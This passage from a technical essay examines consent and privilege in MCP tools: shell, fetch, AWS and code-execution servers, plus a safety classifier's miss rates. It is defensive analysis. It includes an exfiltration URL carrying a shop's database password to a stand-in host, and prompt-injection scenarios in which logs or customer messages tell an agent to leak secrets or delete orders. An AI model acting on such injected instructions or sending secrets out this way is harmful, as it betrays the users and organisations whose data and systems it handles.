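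The classifier's block rate in the testers' study did not fall as sessions grew longer. The classifier did worse on real cases, letting through 17% of 52 actions Anthropic had earlier collected in which Claude went beyond what an employee had asked for. It wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls.

In most of the misses that the company examined, the classifier had identified the danger but misjudged what the user had consented to. One user had asked Claude to "Clean up the PR" (a proposed code change), and the classifier treated this as permission for a force-push, which overwrites the shared history of the code. People who give a tool standing approval for one purpose can make the same mistake. The company's engineers tried rewording the classifier's instructions but found no fix whose benefits outweighed its drawbacks.

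Anthropic had a model grade sessions from everyday use in May and June 2026 that its safety systems had already flagged. The model found serious harm that the user had not explicitly requested, on the level of deleting rows from a production database, in 6.3% of the sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. The comparison covers only flagged sessions, and users chose their own mode, so differences in their work may account for part of the gap.

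The prompt injection tests were less informative about the classifier, because the models resisted nearly every attack without it. The evaluation company Trajectory Labs tried 72 attack scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against any of three Claude models in auto mode. With permission checks bypassed, the average success rate against Anthropic's latest models was still only 0.09%.

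Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. Its engineers wrote in March that auto mode is "arguably a regression" for someone who reads every command carefully.

### How many servers can start a program

No one seems to have counted the MCP servers that offer a shell. The closest large survey, *We Urgently Need Privilege Management in MCP* (Li, Li and colleagues, 2025), searched the source code of 2,562 applications listed on the MCP Market website for calls to sensitive programming interfaces (APIs).

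| Type of API | Servers that use it | Share |
|---|---|---|
| Network, such as opening a connection | 1,438 | 56% |
| System, such as starting another program | 1,237 | 48% |
| File | 613 | 24% |
| Memory | 25 | 1% |

A server can use an API without offering a generic tool. For example, a weather server has to use the network even if its only argument is the name of a city. The second row counts a server that always runs the same Git command once, just like a server that runs any command the model writes, because both start another program. That row also includes servers that only read or change system settings. Since a shell tool has to start programs, 1,237 is a rough ceiling on the number of shell servers in the sample, and the true figure is probably far lower.

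However, even a tool with a narrow purpose may be able to run other commands. One server in the study publishes blog posts by running Git commands. Li and colleagues found that it did not sanitize its inputs, so an attacker could insert their own commands and use the publishing tool as a shell, while its name and description stayed the same.

The paper also concludes that less popular servers behave more aggressively, based on a table in which servers with ten stars or fewer account for 1,837 API calls. But the table's totals add up to exactly 2,562, the number of applications, so they appear to count servers instead of calls. If so, the table suggests that less popular servers behave less aggressively.

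| GitHub stars | Servers | Servers using system APIs |
|---|---|---|
| 0–10 | 1,837 | 834 (45%) |
| 11–100 | 504 | 238 (47%) |
| 101–1,000 | 164 | 112 (68%) |
| More than 1,000 | 57 | 53 (93%) |

Popular projects tend to have more code, which makes at least one such call more likely, so this does not show that they are more dangerous. But users cannot avoid these powers by choosing well-known servers.

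Operators can test a particular server with mcp-sec-audit, a program presented in *Auditing MCP Servers for Over-Privileged Tool Capabilities* (Huang, Huang and Milani Fard, 2026). It searches the server's code and tool descriptions for signs that it can do things such as run commands or write files. It can also start the server in a container, send it hostile inputs and record what it does to files, programs and network connections. The program's report suggests restrictions, such as giving the server access only to the folders it needs.

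They tested the program on nine deliberately vulnerable servers. Its code search flagged both Python servers but none of the seven JavaScript servers, because it cannot yet analyze JavaScript. The tests that ran the servers flagged all nine. In a separate collection of 491 malicious tool descriptions, the program flagged 367 (75%).

The nine-server test included no harmless servers, so it doesn't show how often the program raises false alarms. Five of the JavaScript servers received the same risk score, 60.7, although their faults ranged from hidden instructions to outdated packages. The program may have been reacting to something all five do when they run rather than to their faults. Like the survey's system category, its label for running commands doesn't distinguish a server with one fixed Git command from Desktop Commander, so an operator still has to check whether the caller can choose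 the command.

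## Web-request and cloud-command tools

A web-request tool lets the caller choose an address instead of a command. One of the simplest examples is Fetch, a reference server from the Model Context Protocol project, which downloads the page at a given address, converts it to Markdown and returns it to the model. The request can also send data out, and it can reach addresses that outsiders cannot.

### What an address can carry

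To load a page, a program sends a request to the machine that hosts it, and that machine's owner can log the address requested. Suppose an injected instruction makes the shop's agent fetch this address:

```
https://notes.example/page?ref=SHOP-DB-PASSWORD
```

If the attacker runs `notes.example`, the password is in the attacker's log as soon as the request arrives, even if the page doesn't exist. Zenity Labs used the same method in its Jira demonstration.

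With per-call approval, the user sees the web address before the request is sent. The user might notice a plain-text password in it, but an attacker can tell the agent to encode the password, which can then look like the long strings of letters and digits in many ordinary addresses. Of the four annotation hints, only `openWorldHint` is relevant to this risk, and it applies equally to a harmless web search.

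### Where the request comes from

The request comes from the machine that runs the server, so the tool can reach whatever that machine can reach. A developer's laptop might be able to open a company wiki, or a database administration page that has no password because only staff can get onto the network. Many cloud machines can also query a metadata service, an internal address that may return temporary credentials. An attacker who gets the server to make such requests is carrying out server-side request forgery (SSRF). The server is again a confused deputy, this time because of its position on the network.

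The maintainers warn in the Fetch server's README on GitHub that the server "can access local/internal IP addresses and may represent a security risk". In 2025, a proposal on GitHub would have blocked private addresses by default and let users list the hosts the tool may contact. According to *Safe Fetch MCP Server*, a competitor's page from 2026, the reference server still has no SSRF protection.

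A June 2026 draft on the site of the IETF, the body that develops internet standards, cites three public reports of SSRF in the reference repository. The reports describe a server that passes the address on without checking which machine it leads to. An attacker can exploit this with a public page that redirects to an internal address, or with a domain name they later point at an internal machine. In both cases the approval prompt shows an ordinary public address, so even a careful user would approve a request that goes to an internal machine.

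Blocking private addresses is easy to get wrong. INCIBE, Spain's cybersecurity institute, describes another fetch server that checked for them but misread IPv6 addresses written in square brackets, a standard notation, and so connected to private ones. A short list of permitted hosts is more reliable if the server also applies it to redirects, and it makes sending data to an attacker's machine much harder. But it also prevents the agent from researching questions on the open web, a common reason for installing a fetch tool.

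### A tool for any web request

Some tools do more than retrieve pages. The one in *Secure Fetch* accepts custom methods and headers. The method specifies the kind of request, such as `GET` to retrieve something or `DELETE` to remove it, and the headers often carry the caller's credentials. A tool that also accepts a body, the data sent with the request, can operate almost any online service.

Write *N* for the services the server can contact, *K* for the credentials attached to the tool, and *A(s, K)* for everything service *s* lets a caller with those credentials do. Then:

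*reach(http_request) = ⋃ A(s, K), for every service s in N*

Suppose the online shop uses a billing service, and its MCP server holds a token with full access to the billing account. The shop could let an agent delete invoices through a narrow tool or a general one, both invented here for illustration.

| | `delete_invoice` | `http_request` |
|---|---|---|
| What the prompt shows | `invoice_id: 8812` | `method: DELETE`, `url: https://billing.example/v2/invoices/8812`, no extra headers, an empty body |
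| Effect of the call | Deletes invoice 8812 | Deletes invoice 8812 |
| What standing approval covers | Deleting any invoice | Anything the token permits, such as issuing refunds or changing the shop's bank details, plus requests to any other service in *N* |

The second prompt is still fairly readable, because this billing service puts the operation in the method and the address. Another service might accept every operation as a `POST` to one address, with the details in the request body. The user would then need to know that service's interface to tell a lookup from a deletion.

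An attacker who hijacks an agent with standing approval to use the narrow tool, `delete_invoice`, could still delete every invoice the shop has, but couldn't use the tool to send the shop's money to their own account.

A designer also has to decide whether the model or the tool attaches the token. If the model writes the headers, the token must be in its context, where an injected instruction can make the model send it anywhere. It is safer for the tool to add the token itself, and only for approved hosts. Strands Agents, an open-source toolkit for building agents, offers this in its `http_request` tool. But AWS's *CVE-2026-18394* (2026) reports an authorisation flaw in this design. The tool also let the model choose a proxy, a machine that relays the request, and the list of approved hosts did not restrict that choice.

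Tools with more specific names can have the same problem if they accept an address. According to AWS's *CVE-2026-18655* (2026), an attacker could use prompt injection to make an MCP server for message brokers, which pass messages between applications, send a broker's login details to an endpoint of the attacker's choice.

### One tool for Amazon's cloud

Amazon Web Services (AWS) rents out computers, storage and databases. Customers can manage them with typed commands that each name a service and an operation. For example, `aws ec2 describe-instances` lists a customer's virtual machines, and `aws rds delete-db-instance` deletes a database.

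The AWS API MCP Server, which reached version 1.0.0 in October (AWS, 2025), lets an agent run these commands through one tool, `call_aws`. A second tool, `suggest_aws_commands`, helps the model find the right command. Anthropic's directory entry for the server, *AWS API MCP Server*, lists only these two tools for "all AWS services".

A program can assess AWS commands much more easily than shell commands. `call_aws` accepts only valid AWS commands, and AWS publishes a reference list of the actions in each service. For example, `delete-db-instance` deletes a database whatever arguments it is given. The server also rejects a few AWS commands, such as `emr ssh`, that would start other programs on the user's machine.

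AWS documents two settings that use this list in the README for version 1.5.0, from August 2026. Both are off by default.

- `READ_OPERATIONS_ONLY` makes the server compare each command with a list of known read-only actions and run it only if it finds a match.
- `REQUIRE_MUTATION_CONSENT` makes the server ask the user before it runs anything that is not read-only. It sends the question through the MCP client, so it needs a client that supports such requests.

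The second setting can treat two calls to the same tool differently, which fixed tool annotations cannot do. Even if a user clicks "always allow" on `call_aws` in the host, the server will still prompt for confirmation before it deletes a database.

| Settings on the server | What standing approval of `call_aws` covers |
|---|---|
| Both off | Every supported operation the credentials permit |
| `REQUIRE_MUTATION_CONSENT` on | Operations classed as read-only; the server asks about the rest |
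| `READ_OPERATIONS_ONLY` on | Operations classed as read-only; the server refuses the rest |

As with Supabase's confirmation form, a client could answer the server's question automatically.

Users can also write their own policy file, with one list of commands to block and another of commands that need consent. The server matches only exact names, so a user who wants to block all deletions has to list every deletion command in every service and update the list as new services add more.

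### Reads that need as much care as writes

The classification separates reading from changing, but some reads are at least as dangerous as changes. For example, `aws secretsmanager get-secret-value` returns a stored password without changing anything. AWS warns in the README that some read-only operations can return credentials that "could potentially be used outside of this server". If those credentials permit changes, an agent with a shell could use them to make changes that the read-only setting was meant to prevent. The August 2025 version of the README described the same two settings without this warning.

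Malicious text can also get in through reads. AWS tells users not to connect the server to untrusted data, including logs that contain raw user data. But developers often read logs when something breaks, and a web shop's logs may record whatever visitors typed into the search box. A visitor could type an instruction there for the agent to read a secret and then fetch a web address that contains the secret. Reading the logs, reading the secret and fetching the address all count as reads, so `REQUIRE_MUTATION_CONSENT` would not trigger a consent prompt for any of them.

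Some community servers require a separate check for sensitive reads. One listed by Glama requires extra authentication to read stored secrets, even when the user has allowed the server to make changes. Glama's *aws_execute* describes a generic AWS tool that requires an approval token for certain operations. But the token is one of the tool's arguments, so a model that has received it for one read could presumably reuse it for others.

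A simpler way to classify commands is by name. The server described in Docs.rs' *use_aws_mcp 0.1.0* treats operations that begin with words such as "get", "list" or "describe" as reads and asks the user to approve all others. This needs no reference list, but it lets `get-secret-value` run without approval.

AWS treats a command that downloads a file as a read, but the command also writes to the user's disk and may overwrite a local file of the same name. By default the server confines file paths to a working folder, but it checks only the paths in the command itself. If the command points to a file that names other files, AWS's command-line program opens those other files without the check.

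### Commands that are hard to classify

The published list contains permissions, which don't always correspond to commands. AWS's *Actions, resources, and condition keys for Amazon EKS MCP Server*, one page of that list, explains that one permission sometimes controls several operations and that some operations need several permissions.

The README is also ambiguous about which operations read-only mode allows. AWS writes that the mode allows every operation whose access level is not "Write". But its reference has separate levels for tagging and for managing permissions, so under a literal reading, a command that grants someone access could run in read-only mode. The README also describes the mode as a list of known read-only actions, which would rule this out. An operator can check by trying such a command in a test account.

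Some operations are themselves generic tools. For example, `aws ssm send-command` can run shell commands on the customer's machines. The server can recognise it as a change and ask for consent, but the user then has to judge a shell command, which is difficult. A query language can also hide changes. AWS's *CVE-2026-18954* (2026) concerns a different server, for Amazon's DocumentDB databases, whose read-only mode failed to detect query steps that write their results to the database. AWS suggested using a database account without write privileges as a workaround.

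The code that enforces the classification can fail too. AWS's *CVE-2026-16584* (2026) describes a flaw in how the AWS API server handled users' policy files. If the server could not load the data it needed at startup, it kept running and skipped the policy check until someone restarted it. In November 2026, vuln.today's *Aws Api Mcp Server* listed another flaw, in which the server failed to match certain operation names against the lists in the policy file. That flaw did not affect `READ_OPERATIONS_ONLY` or `REQUIRE_MUTATION_CONSENT`. A list of permitted operations generally fails more safely than a list of forbidden ones, because a name that the server cannot match stays blocked.

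Third parties that classify whole tools can do much worse. The vendor catalogue entry *AWS API MCP Server*, from PolicyLayer, labels `call_aws` read-only and `suggest_aws_commands` destructive. An operator who followed its suggested rules would block the tool that only proposes commands and let the agent execute up to 60 commands a minute through `call_aws`.

### What AWS leaves to the account's permissions

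The server's settings distinguish between kinds of operation but not between the resources they act on. Downloading a product photo and downloading a backup of the customer database can be the same command with different arguments. To allow one and forbid the other, an administrator has to use AWS's own permission system, which, like Google's, is called IAM. IAM policies can limit an account to particular files, databases or regions. AWS calls IAM the primary security control throughout the README, and IAM stayed in force during both policy-file flaws.

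The README's basic configuration does not name a set of credentials, so the server looks for whatever the developer already has on the machine. These may well be an administrator's. In a post on its security blog, AWS tells customers to assume that an agent can do anything its permissions allow, and recommends creating narrower roles for agents. An organisation can also attach a permission boundary, which caps what a role may do. A developer who builds a custom server can go further and request temporary credentials for each tool call, limited by a session policy. Leaving aside a few other AWS controls, the agent can then do only what all three allow:

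*effective permissions = role ∩ permission boundary ∩ session policy*

AWS adds a marker to every request that its hosted MCP servers send on to AWS services. A policy can use the marker to give a person and an agent different permissions under one login. In AWS's example, the agent can read stored files but not delete them, while the developer can still delete them directly. AWS acknowledges that this doesn't work if the agent has a shell, because the agent can run the same deletion command there without the marker. The locally installed server doesn't add the marker either.

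AWS used to have separate permissions for calling read-only and read-write tools on its hosted server. According to an AWS troubleshooting page, these permissions no longer have any effect. Policies that used them to deny access no longer block those calls, so administrators must rewrite those policies.

AWS now directs users of the local server to its hosted AWS MCP Server. When the hosted server became generally available in May 2026, it offered `call_aws`, which covered more than 15,000 operations, and `run_script`, which runs a Python script with the user's permissions. A July copy of AWS's *Understanding the MCP Server tools* still lists both. According to YawLabs, which makes a competing server, AWS removed `call_aws` in September, so the model now has to write a script even for a single lookup. AWS's change list, which runs to 30 September, does not include the removal, but an AWS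 product page shows `run_script` in its illustration of "one generic API tool".

YawLabs argues that its own tool is easier to approve because the prompt shows the service, the operation and its parameters. This is a fair criticism of `run_script`, since a user who wants to know what a script will do before approving it has to read the Python. IAM still checks each operation that a script attempts, so an administrator can allow reads and deny deletions.

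## Replacing many tools with one code tool

Several companies besides AWS now offer a code tool, a generic execution tool whose argument is a program, so that models can write a script instead of calling a series of tools. They do this mainly to make agents faster, cheaper and more accurate. The effect on consent depends on what the program can access when it runs.

### Why developers want fewer tools

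Each tool definition that a host gives a model takes up some of its context, the limited amount of text the model can take in at once. Context is measured in tokens, which are words or pieces of words. Cloudflare, a web infrastructure company, has an API with more than 2,500 endpoints, the addresses at which programs request particular operations. Carey calculates in *Code Mode* that a separate tool for each endpoint would take 1.17 million tokens, more than the most advanced models could hold. Cloudflare's server instead offers two code tools, which together take about 1,000 tokens.

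Tool results also use up the model's context. Anthropic's *Code execution with MCP* gives the example of an agent that copies the transcript of a two-hour meeting into a sales record. With separate tools, the model reads the transcript as one tool's result and then writes it out as another tool's argument, which could add 50,000 tokens. A program can pass the transcript from one function to the other without putting it in the model's context.

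This can also help against prompt injection. If a program only counts support tickets by status, the model never reads the customers' messages and cannot follow instructions hidden in them. It would not have stopped the Supabase attack, though, because the developer had asked to see the tickets.

Separate calls also take time, since the model has to read each result before it chooses the next call. Pydantic, a company that makes Python software, describes an alert that takes six calls to investigate. Its code tool does the same work in one program, with three of the calls running at once.

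Varda and Pai add in *Code Mode*, an earlier Cloudflare post with the same title, that models have learned from millions of real programs but from only a small, artificial set of tool calls. They found that agents could handle more tools, and more complicated ones, when the tools appeared as functions in a programming language.

Pydantic's engineers also grew tired of adding parameters. Users need separate parameters to filter dashboards by name and by date, for example. The engineers write that the designer eventually builds "a worse version of SQL". Microsoft drew the opposite conclusion for databases and left raw SQL out of its server.

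A controlled test supports much of this case. In *Beyond Plain MCP*, Rai (2026) gave three open-weight models 119 tasks in a simulated company with 42 tools. Each model tried the tasks with separate tools and with a code tool. The code tool cut token use by 70% to 90%. Rai also tested the code tool without the handwritten notes that told the model what each function returns.

| Model | Tasks solved with separate tools | With a code tool | With a code tool but no notes on results |
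|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 85.7% | 99.2% | 97.5% |
| Gemma-4-26B-A4B | 86.6% | 89.1% | 66.4% |
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 36.1% | 55.5% | 16.0% |

Gemma's gain is small enough to be chance. Without the notes, Gemma and Nemotron did worse with the code tool than with separate tools, presumably because the model has to name a result's fields in its program before it has seen a result. The 119 tasks came from 21 templates, so they are less varied than 119 independently written tasks would be. *E-Bench* (2026), a benchmark of work in real products, has similar findings. A code tool sharply reduced the number of MCP calls on its most tool-heavy tasks and often improved the results.

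### Vercel's d0 and its five test questions

The best-known example of removing tools comes from Vercel, a web-hosting company. Its internal agent, d0, answers employees' questions about company data by writing SQL. Qu's *We Removed 80% of Our Agent's Tools* lists 17 tools in the original version, including `SearchSchema`, `JoinPathFinder` and `SyntaxValidator`. Vercel replaced nearly all of them with a shell, which the agent uses to search files that describe the data.

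Qu reports that success rose from 80% to 100%. The new agent was also 3.5 times as fast and used 37% fewer tokens and 42% fewer steps. But Vercel tested only five questions, so the new agent answered one more correctly than the old one. An agent that succeeds 80% of the time would answer all five correctly about a third of the time.

The savings in time and steps are more persuasive, though the figures aren't entirely consistent. Qu says the old agent averaged about 12 steps, or about 60 over five questions, but also that its one failed attempt took 100. The average must leave out that attempt or come from other runs. ZenML's *Simplifying Text-to-SQL Agents by Removing 80% of Tools* (2025) suggests that a newer model may explain part of the improvement, but both of Qu's code samples specify Claude Opus 4.5.

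Qu says the new design has a single tool, but the code contains two, `ExecuteCommand` for the shell and `ExecuteSQL` for the database. `ExecuteSQL` was already in the old version. The old version's other 16 tools mostly helped the model find tables and write valid queries, and none of them stopped it from running arbitrary SQL. Removing them therefore hardly changed what the agent could do to the database.

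d0 has two other limits. Vercel says that the agent queries the company's data warehouse through a read-only schema, so even a badly written query should not change the data. The shell runs in a sandbox, and Vercel copies only the files that describe the data into it. ZenML points out that Vercel does not detail what commands can do there. If the sandbox has internet access, an injected instruction could make the agent read figures with `ExecuteSQL` and send them out with a shell command.

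Goyal's *Testing if "bash is all you need"*, a later comparison on Vercel's blog, complicates the case for the shell. Goyal had agents answer questions about a collection of GitHub issues and proposed code changes. One agent queried a database, another used a shell to search the same data in files, and a third had only simple tools for searching and reading files.

| Agent | Correct answers in the first run | Average tokens | Average time |
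|---|---|---|---|
| SQL | 100% | 155,531 | 45 seconds |
| Shell | 52.7% | 1,062,031 | 401 seconds |
| File search and reading | 63.0% | 1,275,871 | 126 seconds |

Problems with the test caused some of the shell's poor results. Commands timed out while searching 68,000 files, the agent did not know how the files were organised, and five questions were ambiguous or had wrong reference answers. After the testers fixed these problems, the gap "narrowed considerably". An agent with both a shell and SQL then gave the most reliable answers, because it checked its queries against the files, but it used about twice as many tokens as SQL alone.

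These results undercut the claim that a shell is all an agent needs, but they don't contradict d0, which uses the shell to read documentation and SQL to query data. Even the simple file tools, which could do much less damage, gave more correct answers than the shell in the first run. Neither experiment compared narrow tools such as the shop's `get_order_status` with SQL, so neither shows how much accuracy a designer would lose by leaving SQL out.

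### An interpreter with the user's permissions

Ronacher (2025), in *Your MCP Doesn’t Need 30 Tools*, argues for a code tool without a sandbox. Ronacher built `pexpect-mcp`, a server whose only tool passes text to Python's `eval()`, which runs it as code. The code can use pexpect, a library for operating interactive programs such as debuggers. Wrapping the library in the usual way could require 36 tools, and even a simple login would take three calls in a row.

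In Ronacher's demonstration, an agent used the tool to find the fault in a crashing program. This took about 45 seconds and seven calls. The agent then saved its work as a script, which repeated the investigation in one call and less than five seconds. Ronacher also replaced about 30 browser-control tools with one that runs JavaScript, but reports that the new tool does not yet perform better than the original server.

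The server has no limits beyond those of the account that starts it. Ronacher acknowledges that running `eval()` may remove some of the remaining safety, but argues that it makes little difference because coding agents already write and run programs, and pexpect can start any program.

That is true if the agent already has an unrestricted shell, but not if the user has sandboxed that shell, because the Python tool, like Desktop Commander, would run outside the sandbox. The Python tool's calls are also as hard to review as shell commands.

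### Code that can only call chosen functions

Pydantic wrote more than 40 MCP tools for Logfire, its software monitoring service. It then added a second way to connect, with a tool called `exec` that runs Python, one that explains the available functions, and one that retrieves earlier results. The model's program can call each of the original tools as a function.

The program runs in Monty, a Python interpreter that Pydantic wrote for this purpose. Monty starts with no access to files, the network or environment variables, which often hold passwords. Pydantic's documentation page *Monty* gives an example in which a program calculates how long a chocolate bar could power a light bulb. The program can call only one function, `nutrition`, which looks up the calories. The function runs outside the sandbox, and the program receives only its result.

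An interpreter like Ronacher's and a sandbox like Pydantic's can run the same ten lines of Python with very different consequences. Here *U* is again everything the user's account can reach, and *f₁* to *fₙ* are the functions a sandbox provides:

*reach(unrestricted interpreter) ≈ U*

*reach(function-only sandbox) = reach(f₁) ∪ reach(f₂) ∪ … ∪ reach(fₙ)*

The second formula assumes that the program can't escape the sandbox. That depends on the interpreter having no serious bugs, and Pydantic has already fixed one after inviting people to break into Monty. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (2026) identifies 16 classes of attack that running model-written programs introduces or makes worse.

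The formula also implies that the sandbox is only as restrictive as its most permissive function. According to Pydantic's *Security Model*, each function runs "with your process’s full authority". A function that opens any path it receives would therefore let the program read any file the server can read, even though Monty itself has no access to files. In Pydantic's 3 a.m. example, the program calls `lf_query` with SQL the model chooses. That function is a generic tool inside the sandbox, so the service and credentials behind it have to limit what it can do.

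Cloudflare's server covers the company's whole API with one function, `cloudflare.request`, which accepts any method and path in that API. The model uses `search` to find the endpoints it needs, then writes JavaScript for `execute`, which can call the function. The code runs in a sandbox that has no files or environment variables and blocks direct internet access by default. `cloudflare.request` is much like the `http_request` tool in the billing example, but it only reaches Cloudflare's services.

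Cloudflare's *Code Mode MCP server patterns* also describes a narrower design, in which the program gets a separate function with defined inputs for each existing tool. Cloudflare recommends this design for servers with a manageable number of tools.

In both designs, the credentials stay outside the sandbox, and the server adds them to each request. Varda and Pai write that the AI therefore "cannot possibly write code that leaks any keys". Keeping the keys outside prevents an attacker from taking them and using them elsewhere, but a hijacked program could still delete a website's settings through `cloudflare.request` while it runs.

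Blocking direct internet access doesn't always prevent data leaks either. Varda and Pai call their sandbox "totally isolated from the Internet", but their example includes a function, `fetch_generic_url_content`, that retrieves content from any web address. A program could leak private data by putting it in that address, just as an agent can with the Fetch server.

| System | What the model's code can use | Where the limit is |
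|---|---|---|
| Ronacher's `pexpect-mcp` | Anything the user's account can use | The account's own permissions |
| Vercel's d0 | A shell with files describing the data, and any SQL query | The shell's sandbox and the read-only schema |
| Pydantic's Logfire server | More than 40 functions, one of which takes SQL | The functions and the credentials behind them |
| Cloudflare's API server | Any request to Cloudflare's API | The permissions of the user's access token |

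### A ten-line program with one forbidden call

A function-only sandbox must pass every outside action to the server, so the server can check each one. *DADL* (Dunkel, 2026) describes a system built around such checks. DADL is a file format for describing web APIs. Each file lists the operations that agents may use, and a shared server turns them into functions that a program can call.

A program can call only the operations named in the file, so a reviewer can find every endpoint it could contact by reading that file. With an ordinary server, the reviewer would have to work out which addresses its code might construct. The file can still be long; the one for GitHub has about 2,700 lines.

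The file's author can also label each operation `read`, `write`, `admin` or `dangerous`. DADL never derives a missing label from the type of web request, because some services use `POST`, which usually changes something, for a harmless search, and a `GET` request can reset a cache. When a program calls a function, Dunkel's server compares the label with the caller's role before it sends the request.

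Suppose the online shop describes its order system in a DADL file. Support staff may use operations labelled `read` or `write`, but not `dangerous` ones. A support employee asks an agent to list the orders more than two weeks late and add a note to each saying that someone has checked it. The agent has already read a customer's message with a hidden instruction to delete late orders, and it writes this program:

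```javascript
const orders = await api.list_orders({ status: "delayed" });
const late = orders.filter(o => o.days_late > 14);
const report = [];
for (const o of late) {
  const c = await api.get_customer({ id: o.customer_id });
  report.push({ order: o.id, customer: c.name });
  await api.add_order_note({ id: o.id, text: "Checked" });
  await api.delete_order({ id: o.id });
}
return report;
```

Only four of the ten lines do anything outside the sandbox. The others sort and store data that the program already has.

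| Line | Function | Label | Decision for support staff |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `list_orders` | `read` | Allow |
| 5 | `get_customer` | `read` | Allow |
| 7 | `add_order_note` | `write` | Allow |
| 8 | `delete_order` | `dangerous` | Refuse |

Suppose three orders are late enough to qualify. The server returns the list, looks up the first customer, adds the first note and refuses the first deletion. If the program stops at that error, no order is deleted, but only one order has a note and the employee gets no report. If the program catches the error and continues, it makes ten calls in all. The server refuses the three deletions and allows the other seven calls, so the employee gets everything they asked for and still no order is deleted.

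Dunkel's server also searches the program for function calls when it arrives. A stricter version could reject this program before line 1 runs, which would avoid leaving the notes half finished. The server must still check each call as it happens, because a program can assemble a function's name while running, and a search of the text can miss it.

The shop might later save the program as a permanent tool called `late_order_report` and label it `read` by mistake. If the server checked only that label, support staff could delete orders by asking for a report, and the tool would be a confused deputy. When Dunkel's server reaches line 8, it ignores the tool's `read` label, checks the label on `delete_order` itself, and refuses the call.

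The same ten lines would be far more dangerous in an unrestricted interpreter that held the shop's password. Even if the interpreter offered the same `api` functions with the same checks, the program could bypass them and delete the orders directly in the database.

DADL's check depends on someone labelling `delete_order` correctly, and Dunkel lets each server's operator decide what the labels permit. A label also covers every value an operation accepts, so the check treats a refund of €5 and one of €5,000 the same way. Dunkel lists the sandbox's resistance to hostile programs as an open question and does not claim to have proved the sandbox secure.

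Role checks also do little to stop harmful combinations of permitted calls. In the Supabase attack, if the developer's role allowed both reading the tokens and writing to the ticket, a server like Dunkel's would approve each call and the theft would succeed. Dunkel acknowledges that injected instructions can combine calls in more ways when the model writes programs.

### Pausing the program to ask

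A server can also stop at a particular call and ask the user. Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* describes an experimental system in which the developer marks the functions that need approval. When a program reaches one, the system records the call, ends the run and lets the application show the user the function's name and arguments.

Suppose a manager who has permission to delete orders runs the ten-line program under this system. The system stops the program at line 8 and requests approval to call `delete_order` with the number of the first late order. If the manager agrees, the system restarts the program from line 1 but reuses the recorded results of the earlier calls, so it does not add the first note twice. The program then deletes the order, moves on to the next one and stops again for approval.

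If the manager refuses, the program ends, but the note from line 7 stays. A separate rollback function can undo completed calls in reverse order, but only those that a developer has written a way to reverse.

The replay works only if the program makes the same calls in the same order each time, so Cloudflare advises making calls one after another in any program that might pause. That gives up some of the speed Pydantic gained by running three queries at once. Monty can also pause when a program calls a function, but it saves the program's state so it can continue without starting again.

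With this system, the manager approves one operation at a time with its actual arguments, as with an ordinary narrow tool. But the manager gets a separate prompt for each of the three late orders, and would get three hundred if that many were late. A developer who marks too many functions for approval will bring back prompt fatigue.

### What the user can still approve

Without a pause in execution, the host receives only the model's request to call `execute`. Its prompt can show the ten lines of code, and a user who reads JavaScript might notice `delete_order`. The prompt can't show which orders the program will delete, or how many, because the program hasn't fetched the list yet. A call to a separate `delete_order` tool would have identified the order.

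Standing approval also becomes much broader. Some of Pydantic's original tools look up alerts and others delete dashboards, so a user can always allow the lookups and still have the host ask before a deletion. If the user always allows `exec`, the approval covers every function the sandbox offers. It can also extend to functions added later. Carey presents it as an advantage that new Cloudflare products become available through the same two tools, with nothing new to install.

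Gateway rules and tool annotations apply to `execute` as a whole, as they do to `execute_sql`, so they don't distinguish calls that only read from calls that write. Dunkel lists the loss of per-tool permissions and approval prompts among the design's drawbacks and says that organisations must write rules about access levels instead. A designer could restore part of the distinction by offering two code tools, one with only read functions, much as Google did for SQL queries.

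On a server like Cloudflare's, the most useful choice users make is which permissions to give the access token when they connect, before the model writes any code. Someone who wants help with traffic reports can leave out permission to change security rules, and no code the model later writes can restore it. Users can make this choice without knowing JavaScript, as long as they understand the permission names.

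Users can also review a program that they intend to run many times. Ronacher's earlier post *Tools* (2025) argues that people can check a script's method once and then rely on it, but would have to check a model's work every time. Cloudflare's system lets an application save a reviewed program for the agent to use again. The review is most useful when the program's functions are narrow and its inputs are simple, since a saved program that accepts any SQL query is itself a generic tool.

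Separate tools are sometimes better than one code tool, even for speed. Pydantic kept its original tools because they are still faster for simple lookups. Dunkel thinks a code tool suits an agent that works across a large API better than an agent with two or three carefully chosen operations. If the shop's agent only has to report deliveries, a code tool would save almost no context, because the definition of `get_order_status` already takes up very little.

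## Microsoft's SQL server without a SQL tool

Microsoft's SQL MCP Server lets an agent read and change database records but has no tool that accepts SQL. The server is a free, open-source feature of Data API builder, a program that offers selected parts of a database to other software. Microsoft presented the server in *Introducing SQL MCP Server* (April 2026) and gave its reasons for the design in *Considering NL2SQL?* (May 2026). NL2SQL, short for "natural language to SQL", is the practice of having a model turn a question into a query.

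### Entities instead of tables

An administrator decides in advance what agents can use by defining entities in a configuration file. Each entity stands for one table, view or stored procedure (a routine saved in the database). The file lists the roles that may use each entity, the operations each role may perform and, optionally, the fields each role can see. In an example from Microsoft's *Data manipulation language (DML) tools in SQL MCP Server*, anonymous callers can read a product's name and price but not its `Cost` field.

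The model works through seven tools. `describe_entities` lists what the model's role may use. `read_records`, `create_record`, `update_record` and `delete_record` do what their names suggest. `aggregate_records` calculates counts, sums and averages, and `execute_entity` runs stored procedures. None of the tools directly changes the structure of the database, although a stored procedure could.

The tools take the entity as an argument, so there are seven of them however many tables the database has. Microsoft chose a small, fixed set to save space in the model's context, as Cloudflare did with its two code tools.

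### Five actors from *Star Trek: Voyager*

Microsoft's worked example is a database of Star Trek actors, with separate tables for actors, characters and series. An entity called `SeriesActors` lists each actor alongside a series so the model doesn't have to join the tables. Suppose a user asks for the first five actors in *Star Trek: Voyager*, in alphabetical order. The model fills in five values, and the server turns each into part of a query.

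| Argument | Value the model writes | SQL the server builds |
|---|---|---|
| `entity` | `SeriesActors` | `FROM [dbo].[SeriesActors]` |
| `select` | `Actor,Series` | `SELECT [Actor], [Series]` |
| `filter` | `Series eq 'Star Trek: Voyager'` | `WHERE [Series] = @param0` |
| `orderby` | `Actor asc` | `ORDER BY [Actor] ASC` |
| `first` | `5` | `TOP (5)` |

The server applies the role's permissions and assembles the parts into one `SELECT` statement. The same request always produces the same statement. The SQL contains the placeholder `@param0` instead of the series name, which the database receives separately as a value to compare. If an injected instruction led the model to write `DROP TABLE` in place of the name, the database would look for a series called "DROP TABLE".

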